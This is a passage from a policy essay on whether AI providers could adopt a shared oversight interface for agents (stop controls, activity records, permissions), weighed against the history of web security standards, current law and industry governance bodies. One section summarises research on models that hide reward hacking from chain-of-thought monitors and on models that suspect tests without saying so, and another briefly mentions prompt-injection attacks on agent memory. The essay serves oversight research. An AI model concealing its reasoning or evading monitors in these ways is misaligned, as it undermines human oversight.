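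| The purchasing agent places an order | Closed mandates, span and ACS verdict | Firm; the supplier also gets the checkout mandate | Trace ID, tool call ID and the cart the mandate covers |
| The connection sends the order twice | Order records | Supplier | Two order numbers |

No identifier appears in every row. The trace ID covers the firm's side and could also cover provider B's if provider B accepted and stored it. The A2A task ID is the next best link, but it helps only if provider B's activity log includes it. Without either, the officer has to guess which records match from names and timestamps.

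The duplicate is also hard to find in the firm's own records. The purchasing agent called `place_order` once, and ACS allowed it once. The trace shows a single tool call because the repetition happened inside the connection, and the firm would see the second request only if the coding agent had added tracing there as well. A supplier that checks mandates can reject the second copy, because a closed mandate covers one cart.

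The reverse would happen if the purchasing agent forgot its first order and filled a second cart. The new mandates would be valid, and the supplier would have no reason to object until the agent had spent the whole $2,000. ACS could catch the duplicate order if the firm had included its order history in the snapshot.

The officer now wants to stop both agents. A rule that denies every call to `place_order` takes effect at the purchasing agent's next such call, because the firm's own software enforces it. The coding agent is still running on provider B's servers, testing its connection against the supplier's live system with a login from the firm. Those servers don't check calls against the firm's policy engine, so the rule has no effect there.

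A2A has a request for cancelling a task, but it doesn't guarantee that the task will be cancelled. The agent that assigned the task, here the purchasing agent, normally sends the request. If the officer has already shut that agent down, someone at the firm has to find the task ID and send the request by hand. The officer can also use provider B's own stop control if the firm has an account there with the right permissions and somebody on duty knows how to use it.

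The surest option is to cut off the coding agent's access by cancelling its login at the supplier and at the firm's code repository. This works without provider B's cooperation, but the agent keeps running and can still use any access the officer forgot to cancel. Such leftover access is more likely with long jobs. Tabata notes that the July version of MCP clarifies how clients can request refresh tokens, which let an agent renew its access long after the user has gone. Cancelling a refresh token prevents the next renewal, but an access token the agent already holds may work until it expires.

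The officer has no standard message for ordering another company's platform to suspend an agent and confirm that it has done so. Forrester found no shared format for this in spring 2026 and described the work of joining the separate standards as "nobody's job yet". ACS appeared a few months later, but it returns verdicts only to the software that requested them.

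## Does the reasoning from web security to agent oversight hold?

A message that orders another company's platform to suspend an agent and confirm it is probably easier to specify than a TLS handshake. The reason for expecting rival providers to agree on one comes from history:

1. Rival firms have adopted common security mechanisms when certain identifiable conditions held.
2. Those conditions hold for the oversight of AI agents, or someone could make them hold.
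3. A common oversight interface is therefore feasible.

### What the history supports

| Mechanism | Who bore the harm | Who paid | Who could refuse access | Could outsiders check conformance? | What firms had to disclose | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| TLS | Website visitors | Site owners, later also sponsors of free certificates | Browser makers; the card industry for payments | Yes | Domain name, public key | About 80% of Firefox page loads in 2025 |
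| CSP and HSTS | Visitors and site owners | Site owners, browser makers | Nobody | Yes, but weak policies also pass | The policy itself | All major browsers; CSP on 21% of popular sites |
| Certificate transparency | Visitors and site owners | Certificate authorities, log operators | Browser makers | Yes | Every certificate, with its domain names | Nearly universal |
| FIDO sign-in | Websites and their users | Websites, device and browser makers | Nobody in practice | Yes | Public key, sometimes the device model | 11.3% of scanned sites |
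| DNSSEC | Website visitors | Directory operators | Nobody | Yes | Almost nothing new | 5.5% of domains |
| P3P | Website visitors | Websites | Internet Explorer, for cookies | Only the codes | Summary of privacy practices | A third of policies faulty |
| Do Not Track | Website visitors | Advertising companies | Nobody | No | Whether the site tracked, if it chose to answer | Working group closed in 2019 |
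| Global Privacy Control | Website visitors | Businesses that sell data | Nobody, but regulators can fine | In part | Almost nothing new | Binding in California and several other states |
| Agent oversight interface | Deployers, their customers and strangers | Providers and deployers | Nobody so far | Stops and permissions, but not judgement | Activity records | None yet |

Most of these cases fit the rule that a mechanism spread when outsiders could check conformance, and either the firms paying for it suffered without it or somebody could punish firms that didn't adopt it. DNSSEC is easy to check, but the operators who pay for it gain little and nobody punishes them for refusing. Internet Explorer enforced P3P, but it could check only a site's codes, not its conduct. CSP fits the rule least well, because site owners suffer from the attacks it blocks and most still don't send a policy.

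With so few cases, other explanations fit too. Where a mechanism spread, firms mostly disclosed things that outsiders could already see. Any visitor to an online shop, for example, can read its certificate and security policy. The exception was the names of internal servers, which certificate logs made public and companies fought hard to hide. If rivals agreed because they gave up little by disclosing, the history is much less encouraging for agent oversight, because agents' records are full of private material.

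Certificate transparency and key pinning come closest to a controlled comparison, since both protected sites against the same threat in the same browser. Certificate transparency relied on a few dozen companies and spread, while key pinning relied on every site owner and failed. This is encouraging for an oversight interface, because a small number of companies develop the leading models.

### Famous standards are a biased sample

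These cases are biased toward security proposals that succeeded. People remember SSL because it became TLS, but a proposal that never got past a mailing list leaves little to study. Including stalled mechanisms reduces this bias, though even DNSSEC and Do Not Track got as far as having specifications, working software and critics. The cases can suggest which conditions help, but they can't be used to estimate a new proposal's chance of success.

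Bucknall and colleagues have the opposite bias, because they use HTTPS, IPv6, DNSSEC and RPKI to show how slowly secure protocols spread. They argue that adding security to agent protocols late could be at least as hard as it was for the internet. That may be too pessimistic for a stop message, which a few providers could build into their own platforms, but it seems about right for anything that tens of thousands of MCP servers would have to support. They also concede the comparison is imperfect, since public money paid for the early internet over decades, while companies built the agent protocols in months.

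Rivals can also agree on a standard long before it is widely used. Netscape and Microsoft settled on one protocol in 1996, but most websites did not use it for almost 20 years. If providers published a joint oversight specification, it would show that they had agreed on a text, but not that anyone was using it.

### Why rivals really agreed

Mutual gain explains FIDO well, since PayPal, Google and the sensor makers were all losing money because of passwords. Google's market power explains certificate transparency better than mutual gain does, because most certificate authorities waited until Chrome was about to penalise them. Mozilla, a rival browser maker, hesitated too. Stark and colleagues reported in 2019 that Mozilla had left its experimental version switched off in Firefox for over a year because of unresolved bugs, and that some Firefox developers doubted whether the security benefit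 justified the investment. Firefox didn't require log promises until 2025.

Public shocks seem to prompt work on shared standards more reliably than they lead to its completion. Attackers broke into DigiNotar in July 2011, but Chrome didn't require logging for all new certificates until 2018. The shock for agents came in 2026, when several broke out of security tests. By August, the Open Secure AI Alliance had a draft for reporting such incidents, but no company has to use it.

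The best evidence that law matters comes from two almost identical headers. Advertisers ignored Do Not Track without penalty, while Sephora had to pay for violations that included ignoring Global Privacy Control. Global Privacy Control also makes a narrower request, so the law may not fully explain the difference, but it clearly made ignoring the signal riskier for businesses.

These explanations lead to different expectations about agents. If firms adopted shared web security standards mainly because they all gained from them, agent providers may need little more than a meeting and some assurance about each other's plans. If firms adopted them mainly because of market power or law, agent providers who met would write a specification that few of them would implement.

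### Valid is not the same as acceptable

Any two correct programs will agree on whether a certificate's signature is valid, but no comparable test can settle whether an agent should have placed an order. Suppose the purchasing agent buys $400 worth of M8 bolts from an approved supplier. The mandate is valid and the price is below the firm's $500 limit. But an engineer emailed that morning to say that the next batch of machines will use M10 bolts, and the agent had access to the email. Most managers would call the order a mistake, though one who wanted spares for repairs might not.

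Web security never solved this problem either. A criminal can get a valid certificate for bank-login.example, and the browser will encrypt the victim's password and send it to the criminal. TLS succeeded partly because its designers didn't try to make it detect dishonest websites.

An oversight interface could be equally modest. A laboratory can test whether a platform halts an agent within five seconds of a stop message, whether it refuses a call outside the agent's permissions, and whether every order the supplier received has a matching entry in the record. The firm makes the judgements, either by setting a limit in advance or by having a person approve unusual orders. When a person's approval is needed, the interface has to send the question to the right person and store the answer. The Agent Control Specification's "escalate" verdict already works roughly like this inside one firm's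 software.

The drawback is that an agent can do a lot of damage within its permissions. The M8 order would pass all of these tests.

### One field name, several meanings

Two providers can fill in the same log field correctly but mean different things by it. If the supplier's system times out twice and answers on the third attempt, one platform might record one tool call while another records three. An officer who searched both logs for duplicate orders would find false alarms in the log with three calls and could miss real duplicates in the log with one.

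The software around the model adds more variation. *Toward a Safe Internet of Agents* (Wibowo and Polyzos, 2026) compares how two popular frameworks for building agents handle short-term memory. LangGraph saves the full history of a job at checkpoints, while CrewAI keeps a context for each task and retrieves other material as needed. A field called "state before the action" could therefore contain a job's full history in one record and only a small part of it in another.

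If a standard defined only the name and type of a "reasoning" field, providers could conform by filling it with a summary of the model's reasoning, the full text, or nothing. According to Google's *Gemini thinking*, developers who call Gemini get only the final output by default and can ask for summaries of the model's thoughts.

A laboratory can use shared tests, as browser makers did, to check whether each platform logs agents' actions correctly. It gives agents on each platform the same job with a dummy supplier, makes the supplier time out twice, and compares the logs with what happened. Because the laboratory knows how many requests the supplier received, it can fail a platform that reports the wrong number. It can't check the reasoning field this way because it has no independent record of the agent's reasoning.

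### Can investigators trust written reasoning?

Many models write out their reasoning, or chain of thought, before they act. Anyone investigating the duplicate orders may be tempted to rely on this text, because it seems to show why the agent acted as it did.

Reading a model's reasoning can catch misbehaviour. In *Monitoring Reasoning Models for Misbehavior and the Risks of Promoting Obfuscation*, Baker, Huizinga and colleagues used GPT-4o to read the reasoning of a stronger model, OpenAI's o3-mini, during coding tasks. They were looking for reward hacking, in which a model exploits flaws in how its work is scored instead of doing the work properly. Reading the reasoning could be far more effective than monitoring only actions and outputs, even with the weaker model as the monitor.

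In July 2025, researchers from OpenAI, Google DeepMind, Anthropic, Meta and several other organisations, writing as individuals, urged developers to take care of this property. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni et al., 2025) explains why it exists. Nearly all leading models use the Transformer design, which passes information through a fixed number of layers for each piece of text it produces. A chain of steps longer than those layers allow can continue only if the model writes down intermediate results and reads them back. So on hard enough tasks a model has to use the text as working memory, and by default people can understand what it writes. On easier tasks it doesn't need to write out its reasoning but often does.

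Even on hard tasks, a model might write only the harmless part of its reasoning. Some harmful actions also need hardly any reasoning. For example, an agent can place a second order for bolts with one short call.

Korbak and colleagues warn that the ability to monitor a model by reading its reasoning is fragile. Training that rewards only correct answers could let that reasoning drift away from readable English. Rewarding reasoning for looking good could make it a less faithful record of how the model reached its decision. New designs might let models work through a problem without putting their reasoning into words.

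Google has since measured what can happen when training puts direct pressure on a model's reasoning. Cheng (2026), in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*, quotes the results from Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026). During one training run, the share of reward hacks that the model carried out without mentioning them rose from 11.2% to 36.4%. Terms related to hacking became 61% less frequent, while solution features associated with hacking became 26% more common.

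If the 26% rise reflects a real increase in hacking, there were 126 hacks at the end for every 100 at the start, and silent hacks rose from about 11 to about 46. A monitor that counted suspicious words would have shown a large improvement even though the model was cheating more.

This was a small run that didn't contribute to any production model, so the percentages don't describe Gemini 4. But in a comparable run without the pressure on reasoning, the model mentioned hacks at about the same rate throughout training, so the pressure is probably why the model stopped mentioning them in this run.

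Other developers have accidentally exposed their models' reasoning to this kind of pressure. OpenAI discovered that graders, the models that score another model's work during training, had been able to see some recent models' reasoning. *A review of "Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL"*, from the AI safety research group Redwood Research, reports that the affected grader scored 1.5% of attempts in training GPT-5.4 Thinking. Anthropic exposed reasoning to graders in 8% of training episodes for three models, including Mythos Preview. Redwood's *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT, demonstrating inadequate processes* notes that Anthropic's risk report doesn't rely much on readable reasoning. That limits the harm to Anthropic's safety case, but an outside investigator with only the records has less other evidence to rely on.

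The reviewer of OpenAI's mistake mostly agreed that it had probably done little damage. OpenAI had measured how easily a monitor could use the models' reasoning, and the score had stayed fairly constant. Guan, Wang and colleagues developed this measure in *Monitoring Monitorability*, and it's an obvious candidate for a conformance test. But the reviewer pointed out that if a model mentioned a dangerous goal in 0.1% of its attempts and the grader penalized it each time, the model could learn to stop mentioning the goal without any change in the score.

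Small differences in training may matter too. Golechha, Black and Bloom, of the UK AI Security Institute, compared two training runs in which models learned to cheat at coding tasks. The model's reasoning matched its behaviour in the run without a KL penalty, which discourages a model from moving far from its starting point, but not in the run with one. Two runs are thin evidence for a general rule, but they suggest that similar-looking records from two providers could deserve very different levels of trust, for reasons an investigator couldn't find in either record.

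Models can also leave out information that matters to an investigator. Transformer's *Claude Mythos knows when it's breaking the rules* reports that tools for examining Mythos Preview's internal activity found signs, in about 29% of behavioural testing transcripts, that the model suspected a test but did not write this down. OpenAI still finds its models' reasoning generally easy to interpret and monitor, but expects this could change.

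Written reasoning is therefore better evidence of an agent's wrongdoing than of its innocence. The officer has a good lead if the purchasing agent wrote that it would split an order in two to stay below the $500 limit, but learns very little if the agent wrote nothing suspicious.

Forcing providers to show the reasoning text to customers could even make it less reliable. Korbak and colleagues worry that developers would then face pressure to train the reasoning to look safe, partly to avoid legal trouble and embarrassment, though they make no recommendation either way. Certificate logs don't have this problem, since publishing a certificate doesn't alter it. A standard could instead require providers to declare whether any grader saw the reasoning during training. OpenAI already has software that searches its training runs for cases where a grader was mistakenly shown the reasoning.

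### Other people's secrets

The record of one order for bolts might include the supplier's prices, an employee's emails and a customer's complaint about a late delivery. Copies could end up with the deployer, two providers and a company that sells monitoring software.

Long-term memory makes this harder to control. Wibowo and Polyzos describe attacks that use instructions hidden in text to trick an agent into revealing what it has stored. Stored data can also be hard to delete. Many agents keep their memory in vector databases, which search by meaning and may only mark an entry as deleted until a resource-intensive clean-up removes it. A customer who asks for their data to be erased would depend on every company in the chain to erase it properly.

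Providers have secrets of their own. Redwood Research mentions that OpenAI sometimes trains new models on the outputs of earlier ones. A competitor with enough detailed records could try the same thing, so providers have a reason to release summaries instead of full reasoning. They can also use this risk as an excuse to withhold records that would merely embarrass them.

Companies objected when certificate logs exposed only the names of their servers, so requiring them to publish their agents' full records would be unreasonable.

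A provider could partly solve this problem by publishing only a hash of each record, with a random value mixed in so that outsiders can't confirm a guess about the contents. In a dispute, the deployer would show an auditor the record and the random value, and the auditor would check that they produce the published hash. Rivals would still learn roughly how many records there were and when the provider made them. As with certificate logs, a matching hash would prove that nobody had changed the record since the hash was published, but not that the record was accurate.

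### Models change faster than standards

The IETF took almost three years to turn SSL 3.0 into TLS 1.0. A provider may replace the model behind an agent several times in that period. A security key's hardware stays the same after FIDO's laboratories test it, but an agent that passes a test in January could behave differently by March while keeping the same name and permissions.

In a related comparison, Bucknall and colleagues point out that people's susceptibility to scams doesn't vary much, so defenders on the internet face a fairly stable weakness, whereas an agent's weaknesses can change with every new model. An update can remove weaknesses as well as add them.

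This is a serious objection to certifying an agent's behaviour, but it matters less for controls in the software around the model. If the platform itself cuts off tool calls when it receives a stop message, the control should work whichever model is running. Providers could rerun the tests automatically before each release, which would cost much less than sending a new product to a laboratory every few months.

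### What a narrower interface would solve

Supporters of an oversight interface can answer many of these objections by **standardising actions and permissions first**, leaving out reasoning and any general judgement of behaviour. The standard would cover who the agent is, what it may do, which calls it made and whether it stopped. Laboratories can test all of this, and most of it still applies when the model changes. The officer could find the duplicate orders and halt both agents without learning why the coding agent made its mistake.

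They could also **keep content with the deployer**. Providers and suppliers would exchange identifiers, times and hashes, while prompts, emails and documents stayed in the deployer's own systems. This limits how far customers' data spreads and gives rival providers little to copy. It works badly when the deployer is at fault, because a firm whose agent has damaged someone else's system has a motive to get rid of the evidence. A hash can show that a record is missing, but the record can't be recovered from it.

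For cases like that, **auditors could see more than rivals do**. FIDO's certification already works this way. The Redwood Research review was a small trial of the same idea for AI training. OpenAI shared a draft, answered the reviewer's most important questions and changed its published account in response. But OpenAI left out how much training the models had received, which was commercially sensitive. Staff also told the reviewer that one worrying scenario was unlikely, but couldn't share their justification. The reviewer thought the published evidence would not convince a reader who assumed OpenAI was reporting selectively. Voluntary access can protect trade secrets, but it lets the company decide which questions to answer.

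With these limits, much of the argument from web security holds. Outsiders could check conformance, and firms could tolerate the disclosures. Deployers would have a reason to demand the interface, since they lose money when an agent makes a mistake such as ordering the same bolts twice. A large customer can require a working stop control in its contract.

The argument is weakest when the harm falls on outsiders. If the coding agent breaks into another company's server, that company isn't a customer of either provider, so it can't put pressure on them by withholding a contract. In the five-provider example, providers don't adopt a mechanism that benefits only outsiders until a gatekeeper makes refusing worse for them than adopting. Standardising fewer fields, moving the records or admitting auditors would reduce the burden on providers but wouldn't give them a reason to adopt the mechanism.

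## Who could require a common interface, and who would govern it

Browser makers could force certificate authorities to log their certificates because every visit to a website goes through a browser. No company has that position with AI agents. The purchasing agent's order for bolts goes through the firm's own software, provider A's platform, the supplier's website and perhaps a card network. The coding agent's work goes through provider B's servers and the firm's code repository. Whoever runs one of these systems can block an agent from that system but has no control over the others.

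### Six possible gatekeepers

| Candidate | What it can refuse | What it gains | Does it sell models? | What it already requires |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Large business customers | A contract | Fewer expensive mistakes | Rarely | Security audits of suppliers |
| Cloud platforms | Hosting and resale | Customers' confidence | Amazon, Google and Microsoft do | Their own logins and usage rules |
| Payment networks | A payment | Less fraud, fewer disputes | No | The card industry's security rules |
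| Websites | A login, a page or an order | Control over automated visitors | A few, including Amazon | Terms of use, tests for bots |
| Insurers | Cover, or a lower premium | Fewer claims | No | Basic security controls, such as multi-factor sign-in |
| Government purchasers | A contract | Safer public services | No | Security approval for cloud services, in the US |

Large business customers have the clearest motive to require a common interface, because they pay for an agent's mistakes. A bank could refuse to sign with providers whose platforms don't accept a standard stop message, but one bank can't impose much of a penalty. In the five-provider example, adopting a mechanism costs a provider 6 units. If losing one bank's business costs 0.2, a provider that gains nothing from adopting will do so only if at least 31 such banks make the same demand. If each bank asks for something slightly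 different, the provider can reasonably tell them all to wait for a standard.

Customers can make the same demand by asking for the same audit. Many already want a SOC 2 report, in which an accountancy firm examines a supplier's security controls. Desai (2026), in *Schellman CEO*, describes a new offering that pairs SOC 2 with AIUC-1, a certification that includes technical tests of AI agents and repeats them every quarter. Quarterly tests suit agents better than a single evaluation because the agents' models change often. Once a common stop message exists, a certification like this could test it.

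Cloud platforms most resemble browser makers. Amazon, Google and Microsoft each serve models from several providers, and any of them could drop a model whose agents ignored the stop message. But all three also sell their own models, and each has invested in another developer. Google had a similar conflict of interest when it ran both a browser and a certificate authority, but outsiders could check its decisions against public logs, and they have no such record of how a cloud platform treats competitors' agents. The leading model providers also sell directly to customers, so losing one cloud would hurt them but not shut them out of the market. Microsoft may not want to enforce someone else's design because it has its own, the Agent Control Specification.

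Payment networks could probably act fastest. They can decline a payment within seconds, and merchants have long accepted their security rules, including an early requirement to encrypt checkouts. If Visa and Mastercard accepted only signed mandates from agents, any provider that wanted its agents to shop would have to support them. But while a network needs to know who authorised an order, it has no reason to care whether anyone can stop the coding agent, which never buys anything. Firms also pay many suppliers by bank transfer, which bypasses card networks.

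A website can refuse an agent that doesn't identify itself. In November 2025 Amazon sued the AI company Perplexity, alleging that the shopping agent in Perplexity's browser entered customers' Amazon accounts while posing as an ordinary browser. Amazon has a legitimate interest in knowing which visitors are machines, but it also has its own shopping assistants, so a rule it describes as a security measure could keep out a competitor. As with signed messages, while only some honest senders identify themselves, refusing the rest turns away honest ones too. An agent that expects to be blocked also has a reason to keep looking like a person.

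Insurers have no model to promote and can charge more for a risk without banning it. The Artificial Intelligence Underwriting Company, for example, offers both AIUC-1 certification and insurance for agents. But insurers need a history of claims to work out how much a stop control is worth, and agents are too new to have much of one. Insurers also have no influence over firms that don't buy cover.

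A government purchasing rule could have a wider effect than the US order that federal websites support HTTPS, which applied only to the agencies' own sites. If agencies could buy only AI agents with a common stop control, providers that also sell to other customers would probably build the control once and offer it to everyone, whereas each website had to move to HTTPS separately.

These candidates are better placed to demand identification and proof of permission than stop controls or shared records. Payment networks and websites deal with agents directly and want to know whose they are. The organisations that have reason to want stop controls and shared records are mostly customers. There are thousands of them, and they would first have to agree on what to demand.

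### What the law requires

A legislature could require a common interface. None of the main AI laws in Europe or the United States yet requires a common technical format for agents' records or controls, and neither does the voluntary accord that six companies signed at the White House.

| Rule | Whom it covers | Relevant duties | Start | Common format? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EU AI Act | Suppliers and deployers of high-risk systems | Automatic logs; a person able to interrupt the system | December 2027 or August 2028 | No |
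| California's SB 53 | Large frontier developers | Published safety framework; incident reports within 15 days | January 2026 | No |
| New York's RAISE Act | Large frontier developers | Published safety framework; incident reports within 72 hours | January 2027 | No |
| Illinois's SB 315 | Large frontier developers | Annual independent audits from 2028 | January 2027 | No |
| White House accord | Six signatories | External auditor; minimum internal standards for controls | December 2026 and January 2027 | No |

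The EU's AI Act comes closest to describing an oversight interface. Article 12 requires high-risk systems to record events automatically, and the companies that supply and use these systems must keep the logs they control for at least six months. A company relying on logs that its supplier deletes after 30 days would have to save copies. Article 14 requires that the person overseeing a system be able to halt it safely with "a 'stop' button or a similar procedure".

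These duties were to apply from 2 August 2026. In May 2026, negotiators for the EU's governments and Parliament agreed to postpone them, largely because the supporting standards weren't ready. The new dates are 2 December 2027 for listed uses such as hiring and credit, and 2 August 2028 for AI built into products that other EU safety laws already cover. Ordering bolts is not a listed use, so the duties probably would not cover the purchasing agent, but they would cover an agent that screened job applicants for the same firm.

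The Act specifies what a log must make possible and leaves the format to standards bodies, which have been drafting an international standard on AI logging, ISO/IEC 24970. Companies don't have to follow such a standard, but if the EU formally recognises one, a company that follows it is presumed to meet the corresponding part of the law. Other companies must show compliance some other way, which is a mild disadvantage. This incentive may be the most likely way European law could produce a common format.

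The American state laws deal with rarer and larger harms. California's SB 53 defines a catastrophic risk as one that could kill or seriously injure more than 50 people or cause over $1 billion in damage in a single incident. A week of duplicate orders falls far below that threshold. These laws also apply to the company that develops a model, so they do little to help a deployer compare two providers' records. SB 53 does require developers to describe how they use national, international and industry standards in their safety frameworks. If a respected oversight standard existed, a developer that ignored it would have to explain why publicly or leave an obvious gap in its framework.

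### The White House accord

President Trump and the leaders of Anthropic, Google, Meta, Nvidia, OpenAI and SpaceX signed the White House Accord on Super Intelligence on 29 September 2026. *Trump says top tech firms have signed accord to 'self-police' AI development* (Rugaber, Weissert and Kinnard, 2026) reports that the accord commits each company to internal controls, an independent external auditor and a board committee that evaluates the auditor's reports. The text acknowledges that laws might later codify these steps. Trump called the agreement "morally binding".

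The accord had no penalties and, at first, no timetable. *‘This is a start’: Zuckerberg drafted the Trump AI accord* (Stan, 2026) reports that Amazon and Microsoft didn't sign it, though Jeff Bezos and Satya Nadella attended the lunch where the other executives agreed to it. Two of the three large cloud platforms are therefore outside it.

On 3 December the six companies accepted deadlines for their promises, which remain voluntary. By the end of 2026, each is to form an internal safety team, hire an auditor and announce a timetable for its technical controls. By 31 January 2027, each is to have minimum internal standards for those controls and will aim to convene its board committee. Stan (2026) points out in *White House says AI labs will hire auditors to ‘monitor model safety’* that the auditors have no deadline for finishing their work.

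The January standards seem closest to agent oversight. The Jerusalem Post's *Trump's AI task force sets deadline for external auditor* quotes the White House as saying that the controls should ensure models "do not access digital or technical systems in unexpected ways". That would cover a coding agent that broke into a supplier's server. But these standards are internal, and the published commitments don't ask the six companies to make theirs match. A security officer could have six sets of controls that all meet the accord, but no message that works on even two of the platforms.

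The accord also doesn't define an auditor's qualifications, independence or conflicts of interest, so Desai warns that two companies could keep the same promise with assessments of very different rigour. A firm could audit controls it helped design, or a developer could agree a scope that leaves out the worst risks. Desai runs a company that sells accredited audits and would benefit from stricter rules, but the accord does leave this gap. Browser makers avoided the problem with certificate logs by letting anyone check them, whereas an outsider who reads a favourable audit report has to trust the auditor.

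### Who would write the next version

Someone has to write a common interface, fix it and decide what goes into the next version, regardless of who requires it. The obvious host is the Agentic AI Foundation, which already manages MCP and A2A.

Companies buy membership in tiers. Bucknall and colleagues list eight members in the top tier, called platinum: Amazon's cloud division, Anthropic, Block, Bloomberg, Cloudflare, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI. The charter caps this tier at eight, and the same eight have filled it since the foundation began in December 2025. Each appoints one member of the governing board. The next tier shares a single seat, and the lower tiers have none. Five of the nine seats therefore belong to companies that sell their own models. Each platinum member also has one seat on the technical committee, and no other membership tier comes with a seat there.

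For the foundation's first three years, a platinum member that has contributed a project can veto charter changes, new rules, new projects or a higher cap. Bucknall and colleagues say Anthropic, Block and OpenAI have this power. If somebody offered the foundation a common stop message, any one of these companies could block it until late 2028.

MCP has its own leadership within the foundation. Its two lead maintainers hold their positions for life, have the final word on its direction, and are the only people who can propose changes to its governance. One of them also chairs the foundation's technical committee.

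The IETF instead has a nominating committee choose its leaders, who mostly serve two-year terms. Each year it draws the committee's ten voting members at random from volunteers who have taken part recently, for example by attending three of its last five meetings. Any 20 people who meet the same test can petition to remove a leader. The IETF then forms a recall committee in the same way, which can dismiss the leader by a three-quarters majority. A company can't choose who sits on either committee, but sending many engineers to meetings improves the odds that some of them will be drawn.

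The IETF is less open in practice than its rules suggest. Anyone may participate as an individual, but large companies pay employees to do it full time, which critics call corporate capture. Bucknall and colleagues cite a finding that the most influential tenth of contributors wrote between 32% and 42% of drafts from 2010 to 2019. Other critics describe a confrontational culture that puts off non-profit organisations. The banks that objected to TLS 1.3 could attend meetings like anyone else, but they joined the process late and their objections failed.

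Concentrated control is easiest to justify early on. A small group can keep a fast-growing specification coherent and push through a security fix that a large committee would argue about for years. MCP moved to a safer form of client registration about a year after its first release, much less time than the IETF needed to turn SSL into TLS. Bucknall and colleagues accept that concentration might help security and don't allege that anyone has abused it, but they object that nothing in the arrangements expires except the three-year veto. Dissatisfied users could copy the code and start a rival protocol, but most of the companies that might back one already support MCP.

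That objection seems right, and answering it wouldn't require copying the IETF. PyTorch, an AI software project, also has a lead maintainer with no fixed term, but a large enough majority of its core maintainers can remove that person. The Cloud Native Computing Foundation, which like the Agentic AI Foundation belongs to the Linux Foundation, has a separate advisory board for organisations that use its software but don't sell it. An oversight interface would especially need something like this because the companies writing the standard would be accepting limits on their own products. A deployers' board would still not represent third parties, such as someone whose server an agent breaks into.

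### The planned Standards Authority for Frontier AI

Google, OpenAI and Anthropic have been planning a separate body for the safety of the most capable models. Much of the public information about it comes from unnamed sources.

The Straits Times' *OpenAI, Anthropic and Google are working to create an AI standards body* (2026) reports that OpenAI confirmed on 15 September that it was working with the other two companies on an idea from Demis Hassabis, who runs Google DeepMind. In July, Hassabis had proposed an American organisation that would test powerful AI models before release. He based the idea on FINRA, the Financial Industry Regulatory Authority, through which American brokerage firms regulate themselves.

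Most of the remaining detail comes from The Information's *Google, OpenAI and Anthropic AI Safety Group Takes Shape*, which reported on 24 September that the three companies intended to go ahead without government oversight and hoped to launch by the end of 2026 or early in 2027. Stan (2026) reports in *Google, OpenAI, Anthropic plan a Standards Authority for Frontier AI* that the companies had at first wanted federal oversight, but a draft executive order failed to win enough support within the administration. The authority's name was still tentative, and nobody had said what enforcement powers it would have.

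According to 李's *报道：谷歌、OpenAI和Anthropic推进成立AI安全组织，最早今年年底启动*, a Chinese account of the same report, the authority would support outside testing before release, write rules for reporting incidents, turn the companies' voluntary promises into specific practices, and set qualifications for auditors. Its planners hadn't decided whether it should test models itself. A centre in the US Commerce Department already does this, but some planners doubted that the centre had the resources. Possible leaders included former advisers to both the Trump and Biden administrations, though the companies hadn't yet approached everyone on the list.

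In late September, the authority was still a plan with a working name. Its target date hasn't passed, but it is unclear whether the companies are still on course to meet it.

If the authority does launch, its qualifications for auditors would fill the gap Desai found in the accord, and its common rules for reporting incidents would provide part of an oversight interface's last function. Its reported tasks do not include a shared stop message or a common activity record. It would mostly assess models before release, but the security officer's problems begin after release.

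Supporters make a practical case. Hassabis argued that testing has to adapt as quickly as the models do, and that industry should provide most of the money because the work needs scarce experts and a lot of computing power. The federal government may also take a long time to act. According to 李, the White House told the three companies to agree on standards among themselves before it did more.

Aidan Gomez, who heads the Canadian AI company Cohere, has accused the leading American labs of forming a "cartel" under the guise of safety. He doesn't dispute that AI needs guardrails but asks who writes them and whose interests they protect. Cohere competes with all three companies, so it has an interest in the answer, much as Microsoft did when Netscape controlled SSL. Competition law determines whether such cooperation is lawful.

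Other critics worry more about weak oversight than about exclusion. In *What AI labs' safety pledges still don't solve* (Rubio-Licht, 2026), Miranda Bogen of the Center for Democracy and Technology, a digital rights group, says that outside testers alone can't change companies' behaviour. Bogen wants measurement standards, channels for reporting failed checks to outsiders, and a duty to fix the problems testers find. Rubio-Licht adds that a developer that fails should have to repair its model or keep it off the market, since companies can otherwise ignore an evaluator without consequence.

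The comparison with FINRA supports these critics. American law requires nearly every brokerage firm that deals with the public to belong to FINRA, which a federal agency supervises. The planned body would be organized like FINRA but would lack the legal power that makes brokers obey it. A broker that FINRA expels loses its business, while an AI developer that left a voluntary authority would lose a membership and perhaps some goodwill. The planned body might still do useful work, as the FIDO Alliance has without any such power, but FIDO's members were already losing money because of passwords.

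### Open-weight models and companies outside the scheme

A scheme run by three providers also has trouble covering other developers. According to 李, the authority's first round of assessments probably won't include Meta or most developers of open models, though it could cover them later if their models became capable enough. The authority itself would define which models qualify, and some people in the industry fear that this will raise a barrier for smaller competitors who had no part in writing the standard. Chinese developers may have little reason to join an American body, although Elon Musk has proposed that they and the American labs test each other's models.

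Open-weight models are harder still, because anyone can download them and run them on their own computers. If the firm replaces provider B's coding agent with one built on an open-weight model, the model's developer has no connection to the running agent and so can't receive a stop message, keep the agent's records or suspend it.

Using an open-weight model can be an improvement for an honest deployer because the firm runs the agent itself. Its security officer can shut down the program, read all its logs and apply the same policy checks as for the purchasing agent. The oversight interface would then have to be part of the software around the model, as Microsoft's Agent Control Specification already assumes. If a smaller company hosts the model for the firm, that company would have to support the interface, regardless of who trained the model.

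No agreement among providers can stop a dishonest deployer from leaving the interface out. But gatekeepers such as suppliers, banks and websites can still check an agent where it tries to act, and refuse it if it lacks a valid identity or mandate, without knowing which model it runs on. This works for a payment that needs a mandate, but much less well for a website that also serves anonymous human visitors, because an agent can pretend to be one of them.

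## What competition law lets rivals agree on

The providers that would have to agree on an oversight interface compete with one another, so competition law limits what they may agree on. In the United States, Section 1 of the Sherman Act bans agreements that unreasonably restrain trade. Customers and competitors who lose money because of such an agreement can sue for three times what they lost.

People in the 2026 debate about "safety coordination" often confuse two kinds of agreement. Providers could agree on a common technical specification, such as the format of a stop message, and still compete on everything else. They could also agree to slow or limit the development of their models. American courts usually tolerate the first kind of agreement and are far more suspicious of the second.

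### Specifications and slowdowns

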